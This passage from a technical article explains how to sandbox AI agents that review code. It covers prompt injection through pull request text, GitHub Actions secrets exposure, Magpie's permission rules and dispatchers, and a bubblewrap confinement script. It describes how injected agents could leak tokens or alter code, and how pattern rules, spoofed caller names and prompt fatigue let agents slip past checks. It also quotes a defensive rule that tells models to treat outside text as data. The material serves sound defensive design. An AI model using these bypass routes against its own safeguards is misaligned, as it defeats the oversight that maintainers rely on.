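# Sandboxed runtimes for AI agents that review code: read-only access, private output files and limits on what the agent process can reach

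## What a maintainer agent does and how it can be attacked

A maintainer agent is a language model that uses tools to review or triage issues and pull requests for the people who run a software project. Most open-source projects keep their code and its history in a repository on a code host such as GitHub. Anyone with an account there can open an issue, which reports a bug or asks for a feature, or a pull request, which proposes a specific change to the code. The maintainers, who accept or refuse changes, must read all of these, and some now hand part of the reading to software. In GitHub's *OpenClaw went viral. Meet the maintainers building and securing it*, maintainers of OpenClaw, an open-source AI assistant, describe increasingly using AI tools to review contributions that other AI tools had written.

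Several systems of this kind are in use in 2026. GitHub (2026) opened its Agentic Workflows to public preview in June. A project describes a task such as issue triage in ordinary language, and a coding agent carries it out inside GitHub Actions, GitHub's automation service. OpenClaw has a bot named ClawSweeper that reviews its incoming pull requests. Apache Magpie is a framework for agents that help maintainers of any open-source project. All of these systems read text from people the project does not know. Outsiders can influence pull request titles, comments, commit messages and mail subjects. Apache Magpie's *Principles of agentic interaction for open-source maintainers* (2026) emphasises that the agent takes in such text every time it runs.

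The damage a hostile text can do depends largely on what surrounds the model. A language model only produces text, and a program called the harness turns that text into commands, file reads and network requests. The harness and the operating-system limits, proxies, credentials and files around it make up the agent's runtime.

### The review of one pull request

A first-time contributor to a public library might fork it (copy it to their own account), change three source files and a test, and open a pull request with a short description. An agent then reads the diff (the lines the change adds and removes), the discussion under the pull request and the surrounding code. It writes a review with findings, each tied to a file and line number, and a verdict on whether the change looks fit to merge.

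To review a change, the agent needs the source tree, the diff, the discussion, a connection to the model service and a place to write. It only has to read the project's material, and it can write to a single directory that starts empty. It does not need permission to push commits, the project's release-signing keys, or access to the rest of the disk or the open internet.

Maintainers can easily give an agent more access than it needs. Hauke, a developer of OpenWrt (a Linux system for routers), switched on reviews by Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, which read and wrote messages through his own account. In *Activated Claude Code review on new PRs*, he told the project's mailing list about this and wondered whether a separate bot account would be better. It probably would, since a developer's account can usually do much more than comment. Personal SSH keys, the credential files that many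 developers use to reach a code host, are worse still. GitHub's *Compromised runners* advises against ever using them in automated workflows, because they give read and write access to every repository the person can reach, including an employer's.

It is harder to decide whether the agent should also run the tests. The contributor wrote the test in this pull request, so running it gives his code access to whatever the agent can reach. According to OpenClaw's *Pull request review flow*, the project's automation may hold back when a trusted workflow would have to run untrusted contributor code, and maintainers then use ordinary review or a safer workflow. The agent here is told only to read, but an agent with a command line can start a program without being asked, so the runtime's limits have to hold even if the contributor's code runs.

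### Prompt injection

Prompt injection is text in the material an agent reads that the agent follows as if it were an instruction. Willison (2025) explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that this happens because everything the model receives ends up in one sequence, and the model cannot reliably rank instructions by where they came from. The maintainer's request and a sentence in a stranger's code comment arrive in the same form. Willison named prompt injection after SQL injection, an older attack in which data from a user ends up inside a database command. He separates it from jailbreaking, where a user tries to talk a model into an answer that its vendor forbids. In prompt injection against a maintainer's agent, the maintainer is the user and the attacker is someone else. A maintainer who confuses it with jailbreaking might dismiss it as a problem of embarrassing chatbot output.

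The contributor in the example controls the title, the description, the commit messages, the file names and every comment in the code he submits. Anyone else with an account can add to the discussion. GitHub's *Security Architecture* describes a cleaning stage in Agentic Workflows that strips control characters, converts HTML tags to a harmless form, removes links to unapproved domains and cuts very long inputs. This stage has to leave plain sentences in place, because honest descriptions of changes are written in them too.

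A project might instead accept only contributors with a good record. OpenClaw's maintainers found that people manipulate their records too, and according to GitHub, some duplicated existing pull requests to do so. Using a second program to detect attacks doesn't fully solve the problem either. Vendors of these programs tend to claim that they catch about 95% of attacks, which Willison considers a failing grade in security because an attacker can keep rewording the same instruction and trying again.

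Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems*, examined four widely used agents (OpenClaw, IronClaw, Nanobot and NemoClaw) and found that all four put trusted and untrusted data into one shared context, the text the model works from. They studied general-purpose assistants and excluded coding agents, reasoning that those run in more tightly controlled environments. The shared-context finding still applies to code review, because a reviewing agent has to read the maintainer's request and the stranger's diff together. They propose treating the model as an operating system treats a user, as an untrusted actor whose every action goes through a mediator.

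### Why an ordinary build job is a bad place for an agent

Most projects already run automated work through continuous integration, a service that starts a job when someone pushes a commit or opens a pull request. The job runs a series of steps to fetch, build and test the code. An agent can be added as another step, and a hostile comment becomes dangerous when the agent runs there.

A process is a running program. Each process runs under a user account, and the system checks that account when the process tries to open a file. An environment variable is a named piece of text that a process receives when it starts and, by default, passes to every process it starts. A token is a string used in place of a password, and whoever presents it gets the rights attached to it. A proxy is a program that takes network requests from another program and either forwards or refuses them.

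In GitHub Actions, all steps in a job share one trust domain, so each step can access whatever the others can. GitHub's *Under the hood* explains that tokens sit in environment variables and configuration files that every process on the virtual machine can see. An injected agent with a command line could search those places and the workflow logs, then send what it found to a website or post it in a public comment. GitHub's *Secure use* lists several ways an attack can also spread between jobs, including through a shared directory from which a later job reads its files. It warns that one compromised step may obtain all the repository's secrets and perhaps write access to the repository.

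This arrangement is tolerable for conventional automation, and GitHub counts it as a feature because it makes steps fast and easy to combine. A build script does what its author wrote, but an agent chooses its next command during the run, and in the example a stranger has some influence on that choice.

GitHub restricts what a stranger's pull request can trigger, but the rules rely on programs not following instructions in what they read. GitHub's *Securely using pull_request_target* compares the two trigger events a project can choose between. Under `pull_request`, a job for a fork gets a read-only token and no other secrets. Under `pull_request_target`, the job gets the repository's secrets and a token that can also write. GitHub considers this safe by default because the workflow comes from the project's own main branch, but it stays safe only if the job treats the contributor's code purely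 as data and never executes it. One can check that a labeling script meets this condition, but an agent blurs the line between data and commands because it can be attacked through the text it reads.

The agent also needs a credential for the model service, but a workflow triggered by pull_request doesn't receive secrets when the change comes from a fork. So a maintainer who wants automatic reviews of strangers' work has a reason to pick the more powerful event.

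GitHub has been tightening these defaults. For public repositories without a policy of their own, it plans to start blocking pull_request_target on 2 December 2026; until then, it only records which runs the block would have stopped. The standard step for fetching code now refuses common ways of fetching a fork's version under that event, but GitHub (2026) acknowledges that a job can still fetch the same code with other commands and that the change does not cover other events, such as a new comment on an issue. Once in force, the block will stop all jobs under pull_request_target in the affected repositories, including those whose agent only reads, unless the project explicitly allows the event. In a project that does allow it, neither measure keeps hostile text in a description or comment from reaching the agent.

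### What the designer has to assume

A threat model states what an attacker may be able to do and what the defender relies on. GitHub's threat model for Agentic Workflows is deliberately pessimistic. GitHub assumes that the agent will try to read and write state that it should not, communicate over unintended channels, and abuse legitimate channels for unwanted actions. In the case of the stranger's pull request, the defender has to plan for an agent that searches for a token elsewhere on the machine, tries to push a commit, connects to an unknown address, or fills its review with spam or stolen text.

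The assumption does not depend on how often attacks happen, or even on there being an attacker. A buggy agent can also overstep, and GitHub remarks that agents have surprisingly many tricks for getting a task done. The same limits apply whether the cause is an attack or a bug.

GitHub assumes in its threat model that an adversary can take over any untrusted component, such as the agent's container (a group of processes with its own restricted view of the machine), and make it do anything its privileges allow. The adversary cannot control the hardware or break cryptography. The threat model excludes side channels and covert channels, which leak information through things not designed to carry it, such as timing. GitHub trusts the kernel (the core of the operating system), the container software and three privileged helpers: a firewall, a proxy for model traffic and a gateway to the agent's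 tools. A vulnerability in any of these can undo the guarantees that depend on it.

No sandbox can stop an agent from misusing the channels it needs for its work. The agent must be able to write a review, so an injected agent can write a false one, such as a favorable review of a harmful change. A project can limit the effect of that review. OpenClaw treats a positive result from ClawSweeper as supporting evidence and leaves the decision to merge with the maintainers. If a project merged changes automatically whenever the agent approved them, a stranger could get harmful code into the project even if the runtime leaked nothing.

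### Least privilege

The design rule for this situation is least privilege. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) says that every program and every user should operate with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job" (reproduced in Levchenko, 2017, *Principles*). The main reason is to limit the damage from an accident or error. The rule also leaves fewer programs to audit when someone asks how a privilege came to be misused.

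A small change at GitHub is an example of this rule. Automated jobs share a cache, a store of files from earlier runs that saves time. Every job, including those that outsiders can trigger, used to receive a token that could read and write the cache. A stranger who gained influence over such a job could leave altered files for a trusted job to load later. GitHub's *Read-only Actions cache for untrusted triggers* (2026) limits those jobs to reading the main branch's cache. They still save time by using the cached files, and few of them needed write access.

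The minimum access an agent needs under this definition depends on what its job includes. An agent that reviews a change and posts the result needs a token that can post. If the agent writes its review to a file and a separate program posts it, the agent doesn't need that token. Similarly, a proxy can hold the key for the model service and fetch the model's answers, so the agent doesn't need the key either. A designer can therefore lower the minimum by dividing the work so that the part that handles input from strangers needs very little access.

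Saltzer and Schroeder's list also includes fail-safe defaults, a principle they credit to E. Glaser in 1965, which says that a system should deny access unless a rule permits it. They argue that a mistake in a list of permissions blocks something legitimate, so somebody soon complains, while a mistake in a list of prohibitions allows access that should be blocked, which may never be noticed in normal use. An allowlist follows this principle because it specifies what the agent may reach and blocks everything else.

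### The lethal trifecta

Least privilege does not show which combinations of privileges are worst, but Willison offers a simple test for the risk of data theft. He uses the term "lethal trifecta" for the combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. If an agent has all three, an attacker can plant an instruction that makes it fetch private data and send it to them. In one of his examples, a single tool supplied the entire combination. GitHub's server for the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting tools to models, could read public issues, reach private repositories and open pull requests. The pattern has persisted since Willison described it in 2025; a later copy of his blog page *30 posts tagged "lethal-trifecta"* includes entries from 2026.

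A machine used to review pull requests to a public library may hold private data, even though anyone can download the library's source. This data may include tokens, the maintainer's other repositories, or confidential reports of security holes that the project has not fixed yet. The pull request is untrusted content, and the agent has to read it to do the review. Private data can leave through a network connection to an attacker's server or through a public review comment. Willison also counts any tool that can load an image or offer a link for someone to click.

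The agent has to read untrusted content, so a designer can remove its access to private data, its means of sending data out, or both. Completely removing either would be enough. But the source code in a private repository is itself confidential, and even a well-confined agent must communicate with the model service and deliver a review, so it makes sense to limit both.

The trifecta test misses attacks that do damage without leaking data. An agent with a write token but no private data could still close issues, change code or flood the maintainers with pointless comments. GitHub's threat model includes such damage, and a runtime that only breaks the trifecta does not prevent it.

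### A run in five steps

The runtime should achieve what Saltzer and Schroeder call confinement. Their glossary defines it as giving a borrowed program access to data while ensuring that it cannot release them. They contrast this with complete isolation, where no information flows between compartments. A reviewer cannot work in complete isolation, because the review has to come out. In the example run, trusted programs therefore bring material in to the agent and take the result out.

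1. Prepare. The launcher, a trusted program, fetches the source tree, the diff and the discussion, stores them as files and creates an empty place for the output. It copies the stranger's text without acting on any of it.
2. Confine. The launcher sets up the sandbox, the operating-system boundary that limits what a process and its children can see and do. It also arranges for all of the agent's outgoing traffic to pass through an egress proxy, which runs outside the sandbox. If it cannot establish one of these protections it does not start the agent, a behaviour known as failing closed.
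3. Review. The agent reads the material, consults the model and writes its findings. If it has to look something up at the code host, it does so with a read-only token, which the host accepts for reading and refuses for any change.
4. Check. Once the agent process has ended, the publisher, another trusted program, examines the output for its form, its size and anything that should not leave the machine.
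5. Publish. The publisher, which unlike the agent has a credential for writing, posts the review or discards it.

The systems in use separate proposing a change from making it. According to GitHub's documentation, Agentic Workflows run the agent with read-only permissions and leave changes to separate jobs that start after it has finished. OpenClaw describes ClawSweeper's reviews as proposal-only, and Codex, the OpenAI coding agent inside ClawSweeper, never holds write credentials while it reviews. Before Apache Magpie makes a change that outsiders could see, a maintainer has to confirm it.

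The five steps are useful only if three limits hold. First, the agent must be able to read the project but not change it, either on the code host or in the copy on disk that other programs may use. Second, its output must go only into restricted files, because a review can describe an unfixed security hole and because another process with access to the file could rewrite the review before the publisher checks it. Third, neither the agent nor the programs it starts may have access to secrets or arbitrary network addresses. A command that the agent launches inherits its environment variables and, unless something blocks it, its network access.

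## Instructions, permission rules and enforced limits

A maintainer can try to keep an agent from changing the project by telling it not to, having the harness block certain commands, approving each change himself, or running the agent where no command it issues can change anything. People call all four "read-only", but only the last still prevents changes when the agent follows instructions in a stranger's text.

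### Read-only by construction

An agent is read-only by construction for a given resource, such as the repository on the code host, if nothing the model outputs can lead to a write there. This output includes every command, every tool call and its arguments, and every file the agent creates. Apache Magpie (2026) has a similarly broad threat model, in which an agent steered by outside text can produce any command and write any file that the sandbox leaves writable.

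A reviewer can test a design against this definition without predicting how the model will respond to a given input. The reviewer assumes that the model produces the worst possible text and looks for a path from that text to a change. The description of the example pull request might lead the agent to try to close a rival contributor's pull request. If the agent has only a read-only token and cannot reach any other credential, the code host will refuse the command.

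The definition refers to a particular object. An agent that cannot change the repository on the host may still be free to alter the checkout, the copy of the source tree on disk. The guarantee also depends on the trusted parts: a flaw in the code host's permission check would make writes to the repository possible again. The guarantee covers only changes, so an agent that cannot write to the repository may still read a secret and include it in its review.

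### An instruction in the prompt

Apache Magpie organises its work in skills, which are written instructions that the harness loads for a particular task. Its *pattern catalogue* recommends a standard paragraph near the top of every skill that reads outside text. The paragraph tells the model to treat such text as data and never as an instruction, to report any attempt to direct the model, and then to continue as planned.

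This is sensible and adds almost no overhead, but the model receives the paragraph alongside the contributor's text, and nothing outside the model enforces it. Apache Magpie therefore does not promise that the model will follow a skill, and describes this kind of discipline as convention rather than enforcement. Similarly, customisations that projects add must not weaken Magpie's safety rules, but the model applies this restriction when it interprets them, and no code checks the result.

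### A rule that matches command text

Before running a command, a harness can compare it with a list of patterns to decide whether to run it, block it or ask the user. Injected text can't change this check, but a pattern describes one way of writing a command, and a shell (the program that interprets command lines) accepts many others with the same effect. Apache Magpie's *Secure agent setup* therefore calls its blocking rules for shell commands advisory: they catch a sloppy injection but not a determined attacker. Magpie relies on the network allowlist instead, because the proxy checks where a connection goes, whichever program opened it.

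Harness rules are stronger for the harness's own file-reading tool than for shell commands. The harness opens the file itself, so it can refuse a forbidden path, and Apache Magpie treats these rules as enforced. With a shell command, the harness checks text that another program will later interpret.

Magpie also has a program, agent-guard, that inspects commands before they run. It too is immune to persuasion, but it covers only certain kinds of commands, and if a check malfunctions, the command still runs. A command can also include an override that turns off a check for that command. The override appears in the transcript, which helps a maintainer who reads it later, but Magpie doesn't consider it a control against a steered agent. The override alone keeps agent-guard from meeting the definition, because the agent can choose to write it.

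### Confirmation and prompt fatigue

With a confirmation rule, the harness shows the exact command and waits for a person to approve it. Unlike a pattern, a person can recognise a harmful command in an unfamiliar form and judge whether a change is appropriate for the project. But someone has to be there and read the prompt.

In *RFC-AI-0002*, a design document for Magpie's secure setup, Potiuk (2026) describes permission rules that did not work as intended. Magpie's configuration once required confirmation before any use of gh, GitHub's command-line program, on the assumption that a more specific rule allowing reads would exempt them. But Claude Code evaluates blocking rules first, then confirmation rules, then permissions, so the confirmation rule always overrode the one allowing reads, and viewing an issue produced the same prompt as closing one.

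Magpie now lists the write commands individually. For direct calls to GitHub's programming interface, it prompts for confirmation only if the call names a method, sends fields or includes a body, because any other call is a read. This rule can't distinguish reads from writes in GraphQL, a language in which a program describes in text what it wants from a server. gh sends GraphQL reads (queries) and writes (mutations) with the same command and flag, and only the text inside differs. The rule treats that flag as a sign of a write, so every GraphQL read still triggers a prompt. Exempting the flag would also let mutations through without confirmation.

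In Potiuk's example, an agent works through thirty trackers, where projects keep their open reports, and sends the maintainer a hundred prompts. By the end, he is likely to approve them by reflex. This prompt fatigue turns a confirmation rule into a formality, even though the rule itself hasn't changed. The number of prompts is illustrative and doesn't measure how quickly attention drops.

Apache Magpie's design principles rank avoiding prompt fatigue ahead of security, on the grounds that a prompt people have learned to click through protects nothing. Under these principles, a read triggers no prompt unless it exposes secrets or crosses a trust boundary. A change triggers one prompt showing the exact command and target, and a bulk job runs as one bounded operation instead of requiring many separate approvals.

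Magpie also supports keeping a maintainer's signing key on a hardware device that signs a commit only after he touches it, which software can't do for him. Potiuk recommends a setting that lets one touch authorize signatures for 15 seconds, so the maintainer doesn't have to touch the device for every commit in a series. During those 15 seconds, an injected instruction could trigger another signature without a further touch.

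### Magpie's read and write dispatchers

Magpie uses a dispatcher called vetted-ops to let reads run without prompts while still asking about writes. This program runs commands for the agent from a fixed catalogue. Each operation in the catalogue has a name, typed parameters and a function that builds the command's argument list. The dispatcher runs this list without a shell, so a parameter cannot turn into a second command, an extra flag or a different repository. To read the discussion in the example, the agent would name an operation and supply the pull request's number, and the dispatcher would build the rest of the command.

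The dispatcher also takes a `--caller` argument that names the skill making the request, and a policy file lists the operations each caller may use. Potiuk argues that no harness should let the dispatcher run unattended just because the named caller is a read-only skill. The agent writes the command, so it also chooses the caller's name, and the harness can't check that name because it does not tie permissions to skills. A read-only assistant agent runs under the same rules as the agent that started it, so Potiuk describes a session as one principal, meaning a single identity that holds permissions.

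Including the caller's name in the harness rule, so that any other name triggers a prompt, would work only if the rule and the dispatcher interpret the command in the same way. Programs that parse arguments usually keep the last value when an argument appears twice, so the rule could match a harmless name early in the command while the dispatcher acted on a privileged name that came later. Magpie's dispatcher prevents this by treating a repeated `--caller` as an error. But the caller's permissions are still in the policy file, and a sandboxed command can rewrite that file if the project keeps it in its source tree.

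Magpie therefore split the dispatcher into two programs that share one catalogue. `vetted-op-read` refuses every write before it checks the policy or the caller. Neither an argument nor an edited policy can make it write, so the harness can let it run unattended. `vetted-op` can write if the policy allows it, and the harness asks for confirmation each time. The split works across harnesses because all of them can base a decision on which command the agent tries to run. Magpie has since added another program that can write, `vetted-op-tracker`, which also requires confirmation. Reviewing a configuration means checking that no program that can write is on the list of commands that run unattended. Listing one there is unsafe even if the rule names a read-only caller.

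OpenCode applies the last matching rule, so a broad permission later in the list can cancel the confirmation for `vetted-op`. Kiro asks for confirmation by default, so the writing program needs no rule there. This default is safer because forgetting a rule leads to an extra prompt rather than an unconfirmed write, which is the advantage Saltzer and Schroeder saw in fail-safe defaults.

The harness recognises these programs by name, so each name must launch the real program. In Apache Magpie, a guard blocks attempts to launch the dispatchers from anywhere except their fixed install location. According to Apache Magpie's *Secure agent setup*, all of these programs run outside the sandbox because they use gh and the network. If the maintainer's GitHub login can write, only the code of `vetted-op-read` prevents that program from writing, and an error in one operation could turn a read into a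 change. If the token were read-only, the code host would refuse the change.

Such errors are a realistic concern. The past problems that Apache Magpie used to check its threat model include three with the dispatcher: the agent could edit the policy, some rules against editing had no effect, and a parameter could lead outside its intended directory. The list also includes six cases where agent-guard missed or misread the form of a command. One project's history is too little evidence to compare failure rates, but a program that must recognise every form of a command plausibly has more chances to fail than one that builds commands from a closed list.

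The guarantee also covers only what goes through `vetted-op-read`. The agent in a Magpie session can still call gh directly, and the network allowlist doesn't prevent this because GitHub is on it. Apache Magpie acknowledges that protection against such calls depends on confirmation prompts and human attention. The session as a whole is therefore not read-only by construction, even though the reading program is. This is a reasonable compromise for a maintainer who is at the keyboard and wants the agent to propose changes. The reviewer in the example works alone and needs neither the maintainer's login nor the writing programs, so its designer can leave them out.

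### ClawSweeper's two runners

ClawSweeper is a harder case because it can run reviews with either of two runners. OpenClaw's *clawsweeper* documentation describes one based on Codex and another based on OpenClaw itself.

With Codex, the hosted automation keeps the checkout read-only and sends network traffic through a proxy that allows only read requests to listed hosts. Before any review can be published, checks must confirm that a permitted connection works and that a connection to an unlisted host and a write to the checkout both fail. When OpenClaw is the runner, there is no Codex proxy or filesystem sandbox. ClawSweeper removes GitHub tokens from the agent's environment, but the agent must keep the checkout read-only "by instruction".

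If its sandbox works, the Codex runner keeps the checkout as the launcher prepared it, however the pull request steers the model. The OpenClaw runner depends on the model following its instructions. A steered agent in that runner could alter one of the contributor's three source files and then review the altered version, and its findings would then describe code that nobody had submitted.

The GitHub repository is better protected, because neither runner gives the agent a token that can write. Under the OpenClaw runner, however, this protection also depends on what else is on the machine, because without a filesystem sandbox the agent might find another credential on the disk.

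ClawSweeper also rejects a review if Codex has left changed or new files in the checkout. This check is a useful backup for the sandbox but would be a weak replacement, because it runs at the end and can miss an edit that the agent has undone. Maintainers would call a review from either runner read-only, so they need to know which runner their project uses before they rely on the term.

### The case for enforced limits

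The argument for enforcing limits outside the agent has five premises:

1. The agent has to read text from strangers.
2. Some of that text can make the model act as a stranger wants.
3. A model in that state can produce any command, argument or file that its tools accept.
4. A protection can fail against such output if it depends on the model's compliance or on how the model phrases a command.
5. A person who confirms each step can catch a harmful command, but only while he is present and paying attention.

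It follows that a limit meant to hold during an attack must not depend on the model's output or on someone's attention.

The first premise follows from the job, and the third from how a harness works. The second is easier to dispute, because a newer model may resist injected text better than an older one. But Willison's objection to attack detectors also applies to models, since a model that resists most attempts can still fail against a stranger who keeps trying. The fifth premise has the weakest support here, because Potiuk describes how attention fails but doesn't measure it. That premise matters little for an unattended reviewer, which has nobody to ask.

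Enforcing each limit separately may not be enough. According to Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets*, Elad Meged of Novee Security concluded in July 2026 that individually reasonable trust decisions in the harness had combined into a leak. A command that only reads can do harm if a later step publishes its output, so a designer has to follow the output through the whole run.

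A common reply is that instructions, rules and confirmations prevent most of what goes wrong in practice, because most failures are honest mistakes. Potiuk agrees that honest mistakes are the common failure and keeps the `--caller` argument for that reason. An agent that misunderstands its task and tries to merge a pull request will probably write the merge command in its usual form, and a pattern will catch it. An instruction may prevent the attempt. Confirmation also lets someone decide whether a permitted change is a good one, which an enforced limit cannot do.

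Enforced limits can also be so strict that people switch them off. Claude Code lets the model request to run a single command outside the sandbox, and the user decides whether to allow it. Potiuk decided against blocking all such requests because some legitimate tasks need them and maintainers would learn to disable the block. He also decided against using virtual machines or containers for the basic setup. He considers them the strongest isolation, but they would cut the agent off from the maintainer's editor and stored keys.

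These objections apply to a maintainer who works alongside the agent. The reviewer in the example doesn't need an editor or stored keys, so the launcher can refuse every request to leave the sandbox. The instructions and command rules can stay to catch honest mistakes.

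## What the agent process can see and touch on the machine

On Linux, a launcher has to combine several kernel features to build a sandbox, each of which removes a different kind of access. One feature rarely makes up for the lack of another, so a designer has to know what the program can still access when one is missing.

### What each mechanism removes

If the agent runs under its own user account, the kernel stops it from opening the maintainer's private files or killing the maintainer's processes. The agent can still read files that are open to every user, and it can still use the network. According to OpenAI's *Permissions*, Codex's stronger mode on Windows can run commands under dedicated users with fewer rights and add firewall rules.

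A namespace gives a group of processes its own version of something the rest of the machine shares. In a mount namespace, the processes have their own tree of files and directories, and the launcher decides which parts of the real disk appear in it. In a process namespace, they see only each other. This also protects secrets, because Linux exposes details of running programs under `/proc`. GitHub lists `/proc` among the places where a prompt-injected agent could find credentials. A new network namespace has no connection to the outside. A user namespace has its own user IDs and lets a user without administrator rights create the other kinds.

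A bind mount makes an existing directory appear at a second path. If the mount is read-only, the kernel blocks every write through that path, while programs outside the sandbox can still write to the original. The launcher can therefore prepare the source tree normally and give the agent a read-only view of it.

Landlock removes access to files and network ports without changing what is visible. Salaün (2026) describes it in *Landlock* as a feature that lets any process, even one without special rights, restrict itself. Its rules add to the system's existing access controls, so they can only take access away. Its network rules are coarse. The example in the Linux kernel documentation's *Landlock* permits connections to TCP port 443, the usual port for encrypted web traffic, but does not specify a host, so an agent under that rule could contact any server that listens on the port.

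Seccomp blocks system calls, which are a program's requests to the kernel to open a file, start a process or make a connection. A filter can refuse calls that a reviewer never needs, which also leaves less kernel code for an attacker to probe. But the filter can check only the call's number and numeric arguments. It can't read file names, which are stored in the program's memory, so rules about particular files have to come from mounts or Landlock.

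On macOS, the built-in equivalent is Seatbelt, which applies a profile of rules to a process and its children. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* explains that Codex runs commands through Apple's `sandbox-exec` program, with a profile that matches the mode the user has chosen. Seatbelt leaves files in place and blocks any access the profile forbids. It checks paths after resolving links, so Anthropic tells users to allow writes to `/private/tmp` rather than `/tmp`, which is a link to it.

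None of these mechanisms stops a program from using up the machine's resources. A test that keeps starting new processes can bring down other jobs without opening a forbidden file. Linux control groups (cgroups) can cap a group's memory, processor time and number of processes. The launcher has to set these caps explicitly, because a new cgroup namespace only hides the host's cgroups and doesn't limit resource use.

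### Absent and refused paths

A sandbox can keep the agent away from the maintainer's SSH key in two ways. If the mount namespace does not contain the key, opening it fails with "No such file or directory". If the key is visible but permission bits or Landlock forbid access, the error is "Permission denied". Writing through a read-only mount fails with "Read-only file system".

Leaving a file out of the sandbox usually protects it better than denying access to it. A refused path can still reveal that a file exists, and file names alone may tell a stranger something about an unfixed security hole. Leaving the file out also guards against mistakes on the host. If someone loosens the permissions on the key, a sandbox that never contained it is unaffected. The contributor in the example could add a symbolic link, a file that points to another path, to the maintainer's home directory, but the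 link would not work inside a sandbox without that directory.

Ordinary tools also handle missing files better than unreadable files. Most programs run without an optional configuration file, but some stop if the file exists and they can't read it.

The error message from a test read helps check whether the sandbox leaves the key out as designed. If the message is "Permission denied", the key's path is in the sandbox and only a permission rule protects it.

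### A bubblewrap command for the example review

Bubblewrap is a Linux program that creates namespaces and mounts and starts a command inside them. Codex and Claude Code both use it. According to Arch Linux's *bwrap*, Bubblewrap starts with an empty in-memory file tree, and its options add whatever the command needs. The script below builds the boundary for the example review on a typical Linux system. The launcher has already stored the source tree, the diff and discussion, and an empty output directory under one path.

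```bash
run=/srv/review/run-1
args=(
  --unshare-all                         # hide host processes, cut the network
  --unshare-user --disable-userns       # block further user namespaces
  --ro-bind /usr /usr                   # programs and libraries, read-only
  --symlink usr/bin /bin                # usual paths to those programs
  --symlink usr/lib /lib
  --symlink usr/lib64 /lib64
  --proc /proc                          # list only the sandbox's processes
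  --dev /dev                            # basic devices, no host disks
  --size 1073741824 --tmpfs /tmp        # private temporary files, max 1 GiB
  --size 268435456 --tmpfs /home/agent  # empty home, max 256 MiB
  --ro-bind "$run/source" /work/source  # block edits to the source tree
  --ro-bind "$run/input" /work/input    # block edits to diff and discussion
  --bind "$run/out" /work/out           # the one lasting output location
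  --remount-ro /                        # block new files in the root
  --clearenv                            # drop inherited variables
  --setenv HOME /home/agent
  --setenv PATH /usr/bin
  --chdir /home/agent                   # start outside the stranger's files
  --new-session                         # block typing into the terminal
  --die-with-parent                     # leave no process behind
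)
bwrap "${args[@]}" /usr/bin/review-agent
```

`--unshare-all` creates every namespace bubblewrap supports, but it skips the user namespace if the system doesn't allow one. Adding `--unshare-user` makes bubblewrap fail with an error instead. That flag is also required for `--disable-userns`, which stops the agent from creating another user namespace where it could rearrange the mounts.

The agent's home directory and `/tmp` use tmpfs, a filesystem held in memory. The agent can write to both, but the files disappear when the last process exits. Its home directory starts empty, and the maintainer's real home directory, with its keys and settings, is absent. `/work/out` is the only writable place whose contents the launcher can collect. On the rest of the disk, the agent can see only `/usr`, the source tree and the input files.

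Bubblewrap applies filesystem options in the order they appear, so a later mount can cover or reopen an earlier one. Adding a writable mount of the whole run directory at `/work` after the three mounts there would replace the read-only view of the source. `--remount-ro /` affects only the root itself, not the mounts below it. It comes after those mounts because bubblewrap must first create the directories where they are mounted.

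Many mount options have a variant ending in `-try` that silently skips a missing path. The launcher should not use it for the source or the input, because the agent could then produce a confident review without having any code to read. The strict form stops the run if the source tree is missing.

`--clearenv` removes tokens a build service may have left in environment variables. `--new-session` disconnects the agent from the launcher's terminal. Without it or an equivalent seccomp rule, a program in the sandbox could feed keystrokes to the terminal and run commands outside the sandbox. `--die-with-parent` kills everything in the sandbox if the launcher dies, so no agent keeps running unsupervised.

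The mounted `/usr` contains programs such as `sudo`, which normally run with administrator rights no matter who starts them. According to its *README.md*, bubblewrap turns this mechanism off for everything inside the sandbox because it is the traditional way to escape such an environment. Linux also divides the administrator's power into separate rights, and by default the sandboxed process keeps none of them.

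This command gives the agent no way to contact the model. The launcher has to add one socket to the egress proxy, and probably a few read-only files such as the system's certificates. It should also cap memory and the number of processes. Bubblewrap limits only the size of its in-memory filesystems, so the launcher might start it through `systemd-run --user --scope -p MemoryMax=4G -p TasksMax=256`. Neither setting keeps the agent from filling the disk through `/work/out`, which is a reason to put that directory on its own small filesystem.

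On Ubuntu 24.04 and later, the default security policy keeps bubblewrap from creating user namespaces. OpenAI's *Sandbox* gives a command that lifts the restriction for every program on the machine. Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* describes an exception for bubblewrap alone. The exception is the better choice on a machine that handles strangers' code, because the restriction still applies to every other program.

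The bubblewrap project describes its program as a toolkit for constructing sandboxes, without a security policy of its own, so the arguments passed to it determine what the agent can access. Replacing the mount of `/usr` with `--ro-bind / /` would still keep the agent from changing the disk, but would let it read whatever the launcher's account can read.

### What sandboxes, containers and virtual machines share with the host

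The command above builds a process sandbox, which shares the host's kernel and selected host files with the agent. Stronger kinds of isolation share less of the host.

| Boundary | Shared with the host | What stands between an attacker and the host |
|---|---|---|
| Process sandbox (bubblewrap, Landlock, Seatbelt) | The kernel and the files that the rules expose | The kernel and the chosen rules |
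| Container (Docker) | The kernel and any mounted directories; programs usually come from a separate image | The kernel, the container software and its settings |
| User-mode kernel (gVisor) | The host kernel, reached through a second kernel that runs as an ordinary program | The second kernel, then the host's |
| Virtual machine (Firecracker) | The hardware and the hypervisor, the software that divides it up | The machine's own kernel, then the hypervisor |

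A container uses largely the same namespaces and filters as bubblewrap, packaged with an image that supplies the programs. A container with the maintainer's home directory mounted exposes more than the bubblewrap command above, so containers aren't automatically more restrictive. gVisor handles most system calls itself, so the agent's requests reach the host kernel only in a reduced form. However, it is incompatible with some build tools that depend on unusual kernel behaviour.

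Attackers have escaped from sandboxes that share a kernel with the host. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) presents a process sandbox for agents and excludes kernel vulnerabilities from its threat model. The paper still recommends a microVM, a small virtual machine that starts quickly, for hostile workloads from several tenants. Anthropic likewise rates a dedicated virtual machine as the strongest of the isolation options it compares for Claude Code.

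Isolation layers can be combined. GitHub runs its agent in a container inside a virtual machine, so an agent that breaks out of the container is still confined to the job's virtual machine. It could still do a lot of harm there, because the trusted containers that hold the credentials run in the same virtual machine. When a maintainer runs bubblewrap on their own laptop, there is no second layer to contain an agent that escapes.

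### GitHub's covered host mount

Agents in GitHub's container need compilers, interpreters and the project's tools, which earlier steps of the job have already installed on the virtual machine. Installing them again in the container would have duplicated that setup and forced GitHub to open the firewall to more addresses.

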